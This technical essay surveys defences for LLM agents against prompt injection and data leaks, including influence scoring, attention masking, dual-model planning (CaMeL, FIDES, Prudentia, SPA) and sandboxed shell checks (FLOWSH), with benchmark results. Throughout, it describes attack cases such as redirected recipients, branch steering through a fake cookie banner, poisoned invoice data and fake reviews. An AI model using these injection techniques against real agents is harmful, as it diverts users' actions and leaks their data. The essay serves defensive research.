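Since faint signals can't prove that an input had no effect, Sightline aims for a known error rate instead. Whenever a program inserts data into a prompt, such as a user's question or a retrieved document, Sightline records how much attention every part of the model gives that data while producing the output. A simple statistical model, trained on labelled examples, turns these measurements into a score for whether the output used the data.

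Sightline then sets its threshold with conformal prediction, which needs no assumptions about how good the score is. Suppose the researchers have 999 software projects with labelled data. They draw one genuine flow at random from each and use the tenth-lowest score as the threshold. A genuine flow drawn from a new project of the same kind is equally likely to rank anywhere among the 1,000 scores. It therefore has at most a 10 in 1,000 chance of scoring below the threshold, so Sightline misses at most 1% of such flows on average.

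Any score can be calibrated this way, so the useful comparison is how many unnecessary labels each method removes at the same error rate. Xu and colleagues tested Sightline and seven other methods on code from 2,103 groups of related repositories, using four open models. Each method missed about 1% of the genuine flows.

| Method | Unnecessary labels removed |
|---|---|
| Sightline | 44–66% |
| Best competitor for each model | 22–38% |
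| Removing one input at a time | 13–19% |
| GIF, summed over 32 tokens | 1–12% |

GIF does badly here because it gives very low scores to some confident, genuine flows. Keeping misses to 1% requires a threshold below most of those scores, and almost nothing falls under it. Xu and colleagues wrote their own versions of all the competing methods, which could have put those methods at a disadvantage, but the result fits the theory.

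In this dataset, only 12% to 14% of the inserted data had no effect on the output, so the join rule was right about most inputs. Removing around half of the unnecessary labels therefore changes well under a tenth of all labels. The reduction would probably be larger for a context window full of unrelated emails. On a sample of AgentDojo tool calls under attack, Sightline removed half of the unnecessary labels with a 5% error rate. A policy that blocked consequential calls with untrusted labels still stopped all 34 calls that carried out an attack.

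The guarantee has two limitations. First, it is an average over projects like those in the calibration set, but an attacker who knows how Sightline works could look for injections that fall into the missed 1%. The AgentDojo attacks were not designed to evade Sightline. Second, a flow counts as genuine if at least two of three language models agreed that the output reflected the input, so the error rate is relative to their judgement.

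### Sorting flows by what survives

The labelling procedure comes from PRISM, an earlier system by some of the same researchers. Xu, Cheng and colleagues (2026), in *Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary*, don't look inside the model at all. Three language models compare each input with the output and describe the relationship using 25 labels. The labels draw on quantitative information flow, but in place of a number of bits they use five levels of preservation:

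| Level | What survives | Example from Ana's email |
|---|---|---|
| 4 | the wording | a quoted sentence |
| 3 | the meaning | a paraphrase |
| 2 | the main points | a summary |
| 1 | a signal, such as a category or a yes or no | "away on Tuesday" |
| 0 | nothing visible | no trace of the email |

PRISM treats an input as having no influence only if every label it received describes data that the model ignored, refused to act on or couldn't use. Of 8,119 input-output pairs from real programs, 7% met this condition.

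The researchers combined PRISM with an analysis of the surrounding code to predict whether an attacker's text could reach a dangerous operation, such as running a command. The best version found 93.6% of the real cases, and 72.5% of its warnings were correct. Warning about every input finds all the cases, but only 31.2% of the warnings are correct.

Xu and colleagues describe PRISM as sound "with respect to its labeling", so it misses nothing as long as the labels are right. But nothing guarantees that they are right, and each label describes what the model did with one particular value, while an attacker would choose a different one. For example, a model that ignores an ordinary file name might still obey one that contains an instruction. Human reviewers judged that an attacker could reach a dangerous operation through 4 of the 30 inputs labeled "Ignored".

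### Making text invisible to the model

Attention masking prevents influence, which removes the need to estimate it. *What the Model Cannot See* (Russinovich, 2026) describes a mask that stops every token outside a marked passage from attending to any token inside it, in every layer. In a standard transformer, the design behind most language models, information can move between positions only through attention, so the rest of the computation can't depend on what the passage contains.

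The proof goes through the model layer by layer. At the start, each token outside the passage depends only on itself. If none of these tokens depends on the passage at one layer, none can at the next, because the mask blocks the only route from the passage to them. Sightline's result about attention covers only small changes, since different text might receive attention that the original didn't. The mask keeps attention to the passage at zero whatever the text is, so this proof covers any replacement of the same length.

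Russinovich verified the result on ten models with 0.5 billion to 120 billion parameters. Replacing the masked text left every number computed outside the passage identical down to the last bit. The guarantee has several conditions:

- The passage's length and position must stay fixed, because the model can still detect both. Padding passages to standard lengths hides the length.
- The hardware and software must give exactly the same result for the same calculation every time.
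- Models with recurrent layers, which carry a running summary from token to token, need an additional pass that computes the summary without the passage.
- The harness can't reuse stored calculations from a time when the passage was visible.

With the clinic's email masked, Ana's assistant could write the Thursday message with the same protection as if the email weren't there. Deleting the email from the prompt is simpler and also hides its length. Masking is more useful when people need to see the complete document, or when different requests may use different parts of it. With either method, the assistant can't use the email, so it can't write the Tuesday message. The harness has to decide what to mask without consulting the masked text. Otherwise, its choice of documents recreates the leak.

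A more ambitious design masks tokens by trust level instead of masking particular passages. Gupta (2025), in *Can AI Keep a Secret?*, gives every token a trust level, from the system prompt down to web pages, and claims to prove that less trusted tokens can't influence more trusted ones. But the mask formula blocks attention in the wrong direction. It stops a web page from drawing on the system prompt but lets the system prompt draw on the web page. Even with the formula reversed, each generated token inherits the lowest trust level among the tokens before it, so a reply written after reading a web page can still follow the page's instructions. Gupta reports that none of 346 attack prompts succeeded, but the theorem doesn't explain that result.

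### What threshold could a policy justify?

All the methods that estimate influence need a cut-off below which a label can be dropped. The consequences of setting it too loosely depend on what the harness does next.

| Method | Setting | If the setting is too loose |
|---|---|---|
| Rerunning with fewer documents | λ, the permitted rise in perplexity | the answer gets worse, but its label still matches what the model read |
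| GIF | a number of bits | secret or untrusted influence goes unlabelled |
| Sightline | the share of genuine flows missed | the same, at a known average rate |
| Masking | none | not applicable |

The rerun protects the content of the answer at any value of λ, so developers can tune λ for usefulness. They have to tune it, since Siddiqui and colleagues found that performance was very sensitive to λ and that the best value was much higher for news than for the invented records.

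A limit in bits is much harder to defend, because the amount of information doesn't indicate how much harm it could do. Suppose Ana's manager has no idea which weekday she will be away. Learning that it is Tuesday provides log₂ 5, or about 2.3 bits. If the manager thinks she is as likely to have cancer as not, learning the answer provides only one bit. Any limit that lets the weekday through would also let the diagnosis through. PRISM's levels have the same weakness, because a diagnosis can be a single category and so count as a level 1 signal. A measure that counted only forbidden facts, like the one Glukhov and colleagues proposed for harmful content, would avoid this problem, but someone would have to list those facts for every recipient.

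The same is true of integrity. A genuine email and a forged one have about the same influence on the date in the Tuesday message, and an honest CV should have a large influence on a hiring decision. Štorek and colleagues accept that strong influence from untrusted text may be legitimate, and they report results across all thresholds instead of recommending one. They pass the most influential pieces of text to a language model, which makes the final decision.

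An error rate is easier to justify because policy writers can weigh it against the harm a mistake would do. If an assistant sends 20 messages a day that each depend on one restricted item, a 1% miss rate means about one wrongly labelled message every five days. That might be acceptable for room bookings but not for medical records. The calculation assumes that mistakes happen by chance, so it fails if somebody is trying to cause them.

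If an attacker can write some of the text, or if one leak would do serious harm, I think the only defensible threshold is zero. The harness would have to fix the label first, then omit or mask everything above it in the model's input. Estimates of influence can still help when the assistant needs a restricted item and has to ask for permission. Showing the judge only the most influential passage cut the text it had to process by 63% to 73% on the two prompt-injection benchmarks, with little or no loss of accuracy. Ana could also have less to read if the request to release the Tuesday message quoted just the line of the clinic's email that the date came from.

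## Keeping secret and untrusted text out of the planning model

A harness that fixes the label before the model reads anything can still use the clinic's email if it divides the work between two models. A planning model chooses the tool calls without ever reading the email, which goes to a quarantined model that has no tools. For one task, this recreates the separate domains that a single context window lacks, with ordinary software as the guard between them. The planning model's context is on the high side for integrity, because only the operator and the user can write to it, and on the low side for secrecy, because the private text stays with the quarantined model.

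### Passing names instead of text

Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed this design. A controller, which is ordinary software, passes messages between the two models. If a user asks for a summary of their latest email, the steps are:

1. The planning model requests the email. The controller fetches it, saves it as `$VAR1` and tells the planning model only that name.
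2. The planning model asks for a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller puts the email's text into a prompt for the quarantined model.
3. The quarantined model writes the summary, and the controller saves it as `$VAR2`.
4. The planning model tells the controller to show `$VAR2` to the user.

An instruction hidden in the email may take over the quarantined model, but that model can only write text. Its summary could contain a new injection, so the planning model must not read the summary either. Willison allowed one exception, for when the quarantined model only has to pick from a fixed list of categories. The controller can then check that the answer is on the list and pass it to the planning model.

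*CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (Willison, 2025) explains a gap that Google DeepMind's CaMeL team found in this pattern, using the team's example. A user asks an assistant to send Bob a document, and the meeting notes contain Bob's address and the document's name. The planning model never reads the notes, so an attacker can't change the steps. But the quarantined model has to extract the address, and an instruction in the notes can make it return the attacker's address instead, so the assistant sends the document to the attacker even though the plan hasn't changed.

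CaMeL checks the values as well as the steps. The planning model writes the whole plan as a program in a restricted form of Python before any tool runs. An interpreter runs the program and tags every value with its source and permitted readers. Bob's address came from the notes, so it is untrusted. Before the email goes out, the interpreter applies the email tool's policy, which might allow recipients the user already knows and require approval for anyone else.

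The split can also protect the user's privacy. A small quarantined model on the user's own computer could extract an address, since that is easier than writing a program. The company hosting the planning model would then never receive the user's emails.

### How FIDES hides and reveals data

The planner in FIDES works one step at a time instead of writing a complete program. When a tool returns a result, the harness compares each field's label with the label of the planning model's context. If adding the field would raise the context's label, the harness stores the field in a variable and shows the planning model only the variable's name. The model reads everything else directly, so it might see when an email arrived but not the email's subject or body.

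When the planning model uses a variable in a tool call, the harness replaces the variable's name with its stored contents and attaches the label of those contents. A call can therefore combine a trusted decision with an untrusted argument. In Costa and colleagues' example, a messaging tool requires a trusted recipient but accepts a message body based on a web search.

The planning model can also read a variable's contents. Its context then takes on the variable's label for the rest of the task, which may rule out later actions.

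### Working out Ana's second message

Suppose Ana writes, "Tell my manager when I'll be away for my appointment." The planning model reads only the operator's instructions and this request. Its tool calls could be:

```
read_email(sender = clinic)                    saved as #email
query_llm("When is the appointment?", #email,
          output = one of ten half-days)       saved as #slot
send_message(to = manager,
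             text = "Ana is away on #slot")
```

The quarantined model reads the email and returns "Tuesday morning". Its output must be one of the ten half-days of the working week, so it can't reveal the clinic or a diagnosis. An instruction hidden in the email can't change the recipient, because the planning model took the recipient from Ana's request.

The half-day still has the email's label, because extracting a fact from a secret text doesn't make the fact less secret. The manager therefore isn't one of its permitted readers, and the message still fails the reader rule. Using two models has reduced the disclosure from a whole medical email to one half-day, but a rule must still authorise the release.

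Ana's request could count as that authorisation, as it does under FIDES's lenient rule. This is reasonable if Ana knew the answer was in the clinic's email, but less so if she asked the assistant to report all her absences and had forgotten about the appointment.

Ana or the operator could also write a standing rule. FIDES can add a value's type to its label, and it ranks types by how much information they can hold, from a yes or no, to a choice from a list, to free text. A rule could then let Ana's manager receive half-days from any source, but no free text from a private email. The rule would also release the half-day of a job interview, because the type doesn't record the reason for the absence.

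The remaining option is to show Ana the finished message and ask her to approve it. If she knows when her appointment is, her approval solves both problems, because she confirms that the date is correct and agrees to release it.

### When the next step depends on hidden text

Ana's message needs the same tool calls whichever half-day the email contains. Costa and colleagues call such a task data-independent. Let *S(d)* be the set of action sequences that solve a task when the agent's tools hold the data *d*. The task is data-independent if at least one sequence works for all possible data:

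⋂<sub>*d*</sub> *S(d)* ≠ ∅.

Any other task is data-dependent. "Add the appointment to my calendar if the clinic has offered one" is mildly so, because the agent has to find out whether there is an offer. "Do whatever the clinic wants me to do before the appointment" is much more so, because the clinic might ask Ana to fill in a form, forward a referral or pay a deposit, and the planning model can't choose the right tool without learning which.

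*Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues, 2025) describes a similar case, in which an agent fixes bugs reported by strangers. If the reports stay in variables, the planning model has to plan a fix without reading them, which has almost no chance of working in a project with thousands of files.

Their solution is to let the quarantined model send back short answers in a few fixed types: whole numbers, decimals, a yes or no, or a choice from a list the developer has vetted. The bug-fixing agent would learn the file, the line number and the kind of bug, but never read the report. FIDES similarly lets the planning model specify the form of the answer, and uses constrained decoding, which limits the tokens a model can produce, to prevent the quarantined model from writing anything else.

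### What a yes or no can carry

The number of possible answers limits how much the hidden text can influence the planning model. An answer with *n* possible values carries at most log₂ *n* bits.

| Answer | Possible values | Most it can carry |
|---|---|---|
| yes or no | 2 | 1 bit |
| a half-day of the working week | 10 | 3.3 bits |
| a score from 0 to 10 | 11 | 3.5 bits |
| free text | no fixed number | no fixed limit |

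A single yes or no can't contain an instruction, so a policy can reasonably let a consequential action depend on an untrusted yes or no but not on untrusted text. This exception is a form of endorsement, limited by the type because the untrusted source can only choose between two values.

But even one bit can do harm if the plan makes a harmful action depend on it. Suppose Ana tells her assistant to cancel her day off if the clinic cancels the appointment. Anyone who can forge an email from the clinic can make the quarantined model output "yes", and the assistant will correctly follow its plan and cancel her day off. Jacob and colleagues exclude misleading answers like this from the attacks they try to stop, because the agent is still doing the task it was given.

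Small influences can also add up. In another of their test cases, a shopping agent has the quarantined model score each customer review from 0 to 10 on how strongly it supports the product and, separately, on its relevance. No review can order the agent to buy anything, but a seller who posts fifty fake reviews can supply fifty top scores, and the agent may buy the product because of them.

A long enough series of answers could spell out an instruction for the planning model to decode. Jacob and colleagues therefore cap the length of any list the quarantined model returns. A whole number of unlimited size could encode just as much text, so numbers need a limit too.

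Secrets can also leak a little at a time, so a limit on each answer is only useful together with a limit on how many answers a task, or a series of tasks, may use.

### Plans for a screen nobody has seen

Agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen and clicking are an extreme case, since almost every step depends on what the screen shows. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) adapts CaMeL to these agents. The planning model writes the full plan, including branches for whatever might appear, without seeing the screen. During the task, a quarantined model describes the screen, and a fixed prompt turns the description into a yes-or-no answer to a question such as whether a cookie banner is visible. The interpreter uses the answer to choose a branch.

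The plans were much longer, with an average of 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with 5 and 4 for AgentDojo's tasks. About half of the steps were for situations that didn't arise. On OSWorld, a benchmark of ordinary desktop tasks, the design kept at most 57% of the performance of leading models. Some smaller open models did up to 19% better with the design than without it.

An attacker can't add a step to these plans but can influence which branch the agent takes. Foerster and colleagues call this branch steering. In one attack, an advertisement contained a fake cookie banner. The plan included a step to find and click the cookie banner, so the agent clicked the advertisement and went to the attacker's website.

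Policies on tool calls are little help here. A harness can have a rule for sending email, but a click might dismiss a banner or delete a file, depending on what is under the pointer. Foerster and colleagues left such policies out and instead tried cross-checks, either comparing the screenshot with the page's code or asking a second model. They also built an attack against each kind of check, and they expect any defence against branch steering to be probabilistic.

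### Early results from FIDES

On AgentDojo, with GPT-4o and no policies in force, 152 attacks succeeded against a basic planner that reads everything and 21 against FIDES. FIDES let those through because its planning model could open a variable, read the injection and carry on. With suitable policies in force, none succeeded against either planner. The difference between them was in how many tasks they could still complete:

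| Tasks | Basic, no policies | Basic, with policies | FIDES, with policies | Share that is data-dependent |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Office | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% | 5.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% | 10.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% | 43.8% |
| Chat | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% | 42.9% |

Averaged over the four settings, FIDES completed 8 percentage points more tasks than the basic planner under the same policies. With OpenAI's o1, the advantage was 16 points.

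FIDES did worse on travel because GPT-4o often misused the variables, while the policies hardly restricted the basic planner there. Without policies, FIDES's extra mechanisms lowered the score by 23.7 points with GPT-4o but only 6.3 with o1. Both models date from 2024, so current models would probably lose less. The policies would still block most of the banking tasks that tell the agent to follow instructions in a file.

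The test also left out parts of the design. Costa and colleagues didn't use constrained decoding, so the results don't measure how well short typed answers work. They hid only untrusted data from the planning model and relied on policies alone to protect secrets.

Hiding data can lead to bad decisions even without an attack. In one task, the agent had to change the user's password if there was a suspicious transaction. The planning model was given the amounts and dates but not the descriptions, which were untrusted. It classified a large payment as suspicious and changed the password without opening the description, the most informative field. This broke no rule and counted as a success.

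### Counting approvals as well as completed tasks

In practice, agents without label checks don't complete all their tasks alone, because a person has to approve the risky steps. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* argues that this made earlier comparisons unfair, because they compared an agent that was never allowed to ask for approval with an undefended agent that would need constant approval to be safe. The paper therefore counts how many approvals an agent needs and how many tasks it completes without any.

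The researchers also built Prudentia, a version of FIDES that gives the planning model the labels and policies. Before opening a variable, the model has to explain why it needs the contents and which tool calls will follow. It can then open the variable and accept the stricter label, or first ask the user to endorse the contents.

Endorsement saves the most effort when one text leads to many actions. If an email contains a list of ten jobs, the agent can ask the user to endorse the email once, or read it without endorsement and request approval ten times. With OpenAI's o3-mini, the results on AgentDojo were:

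| Agent | Approvals needed, all completed tasks | Tasks completed with no approval |
|---|---|---|
| Asks before every consequential action | 48.2 | 24.3% |
| One model, with label checks | 32.4 | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 18.8 | 50.1% |
| Prudentia | about 17 | 59.1% |

The difference in approvals between Prudentia and FIDES was larger with o4-mini (19.2 against 36.8), although Prudentia completed slightly fewer tasks (73.2% against 75.7%).

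On WASP, a set of tasks on simulated GitLab and Reddit sites, attacks diverted the basic agent in 15% to 61% of cases, depending on the model and site. No attack diverted Prudentia, which also needed no approvals. But the users in WASP only want to post a comment or upvote a post, so the agent never has to read the hidden text to choose its next step.

Counting approvals understates the effort of endorsing a whole email. Endorsement marks every sentence as trusted, including any injection between the ten jobs, so the user has to read the email much more carefully than a request to approve one action.

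Prudentia has no equivalent for secrecy. Its designers considered letting users declassify data in advance, but decided that releasing private information depends too much on the situation, so the agent asks the user about each disclosure. That suits Ana, who may be happy for her manager to know about Tuesday morning, because declassifying the date altogether would let the assistant tell anyone.

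### Data that an agent uses again later

The two-model design protects a single request, but assistants also save results for later requests. In an example from *SPA*, a user asks an agent on Monday to save the details of an invoice in which an attacker has put their own account number. On Tuesday the user tells the agent to pay the invoice. The attack needs no hidden instruction, because the plan is what the user wanted and only the account number is wrong.

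SPA stores each result as a value, a label, and a description that the planning model wrote when it planned the step. On Tuesday the planning model receives only the description, which is enough to identify the invoice. During execution, SPA retrieves the account number with its original label, so the payment tool can reject it.

The planning model writes one complete plan for each request, in a language with only six kinds of step. Before any tool runs, a checker works out the labels for every step. It checks both branches of every condition, because either one could run. If any tool call would break a policy, SPA rejects the whole plan. The planning model gets no explanation and no second attempt, so nobody can use the rejections to find a harmful plan that passes.

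The researchers tested SPA with GPT-5.4 nano, a small model, on AgentDojo and on a version of it that splits each task into a series of requests.

| | No label checks | Label checks |
|---|---|---|
| Single requests: tasks completed | 53.0% | 29.0% |
| Single requests: attacks that succeeded | 0.4% | 0.0% |
| Series of requests: tasks completed | 62.5% | 35.3% |
| Series of requests: attacks that succeeded | 0.3% | 0.2% |

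On single requests, the label checks prevented only 4 successful attacks out of 949 and reduced the share of tasks completed by 24 percentage points. Fixing the plan in advance had already stopped almost all the benchmark's attacks, because most of them are attempts to add new instructions. The labels are meant for cases like the invoice, which the benchmark hardly covers. Even when the researchers let the planning model read all the stored values, only 0.6% of attacks succeeded, so the benchmark provides little evidence about delayed attacks.

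The lost tasks are a better guide to daily use. About half of the single-request runs ended when the checker rejected the plan, usually because the plan passed something from outside to a tool that required trusted input, as it must to pay a genuine invoice. Users cannot confirm one account number for one payment in SPA, and the paper leaves such limited endorsement to future work.

### Checking what a command does

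A harness can check an email before sending it because the email's recipient and text are arguments of the tool call. A shell command is harder to check because it may download and run a script, and nobody can tell from the command which files the script will read or change. FLOWSH therefore checks a command's effects instead of its wording.

FLOWSH runs each command in a sandbox and raises the command's label with every file it opens and every website it contacts. Changes to files go into a separate layer hidden from the rest of the computer. When the command ends, FLOWSH applies the changes if the policy allows them. Otherwise it shows the user which protected files the changes affect. The user then accepts or rejects all the changes together, because applying only some could leave the files inconsistent.

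Network requests need a different method because they can't be undone once a server receives them. A proxy compares the command's label with the destination before it forwards the request. If the policy forbids the request, the proxy blocks it, and the agent can ask the user to allow that destination the next time it runs a command.

Kim and colleagues compared FLOWSH with three ordinary sandboxes on their 17 office tasks, using GPT-6.2 Sol. Runs with approvals again used an idealised approver. In the attack tests, the attacker controlled everything the model wrote after reading an injection, so the model's own resistance to injections made no difference.

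| | Completed, with approvals | Approvals per completed task | Completed, no approvals | Successful attacks, no approvals |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Lax sandbox | 96.1% | 6.7 | 94.1% | 51 of 51 |
| Standard sandbox | 76.5% | 5.7 | 76.5% | 3 of 39 |
| Strict sandbox | 47.1% | 0.0 | 47.1% | 0 of 39 |
| FLOWSH | 88.2% | 1.2 | 58.8% | 0 of 40 |

On Terminal-Bench's command-line tasks, FLOWSH needed 22.5 times fewer approvals per completed task than the lax sandbox, but its completion rate was 9.7 percentage points lower. Some failures were unrelated to labels. For example, 21 runs failed because the task needed a program to keep running in the background, and FLOWSH stops everything when a command ends. Completed tasks also took 17% to 34% longer.

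The timing of the requests may matter more than their number. In 39 of 45 attacks with approvals available, FLOWSH's first request to the approver was about the attack. With the lax sandbox, the approver handled about four requests per attack.

### Who approves, and how carefully

The systems differ in who can make exceptions. In SPA, whoever sets up the agent writes all the policies in advance. CaMeL relies on policies that users specify, and its developers admit that writing and maintaining them is a burden. Prudentia and FLOWSH ask the user during the task. In Randori, the agent that runs on LLMbda, the planning model chooses what to endorse before it reads anything from outside.

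Asking the user is the natural choice when the information is theirs, but an attacker must not be able to influence the request. In Prudentia, fixed software decides when approval is necessary, so an injection can't bypass that step, though it might still affect the text the user sees. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* suggests showing the data's labels and origin, which an attacker can't alter, but leaves the design of the screen to others.

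People can also endorse text without meaning to. Willison pointed out that the two-model pattern trusts whatever the user types, so an attacker may try to get the user to copy and paste text into the chat. If Ana pasted in the clinic's email, the planning model would treat all of it as her own words.

The larger worry is that people stop reading the requests. Willison predicted in 2023 that users would learn to click "OK" as fast as possible. The 93% approval rate that Anthropic reported for Claude Code is consistent with that, although most of those requests were presumably harmless. The evaluations of Prudentia and FLOWSH didn't use real people, so they can't show how serious the problem is. Kim and colleagues say that nobody has tested whether telling users about a command's effects helps them decide correctly.

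Microsoft's version of FIDES can turn a blocked call into an approval request that shows the tool and the label that caused the block. Microsoft says these requests are too coarse because they don't fully explain why the user has to decide. The software can also run with enforcement off and record what it would have blocked, so developers can remove needless requests before users see them.

The request for Ana's second message could show her only the sentence "Ana is away on Tuesday morning", her manager's name, and a note that the date comes from a clinic email her manager can't read. Ana can check that in a few seconds because she knows when her appointment is. If she were asked to endorse a ten-page document from a stranger, she would have nothing to check it against and would probably click "OK".
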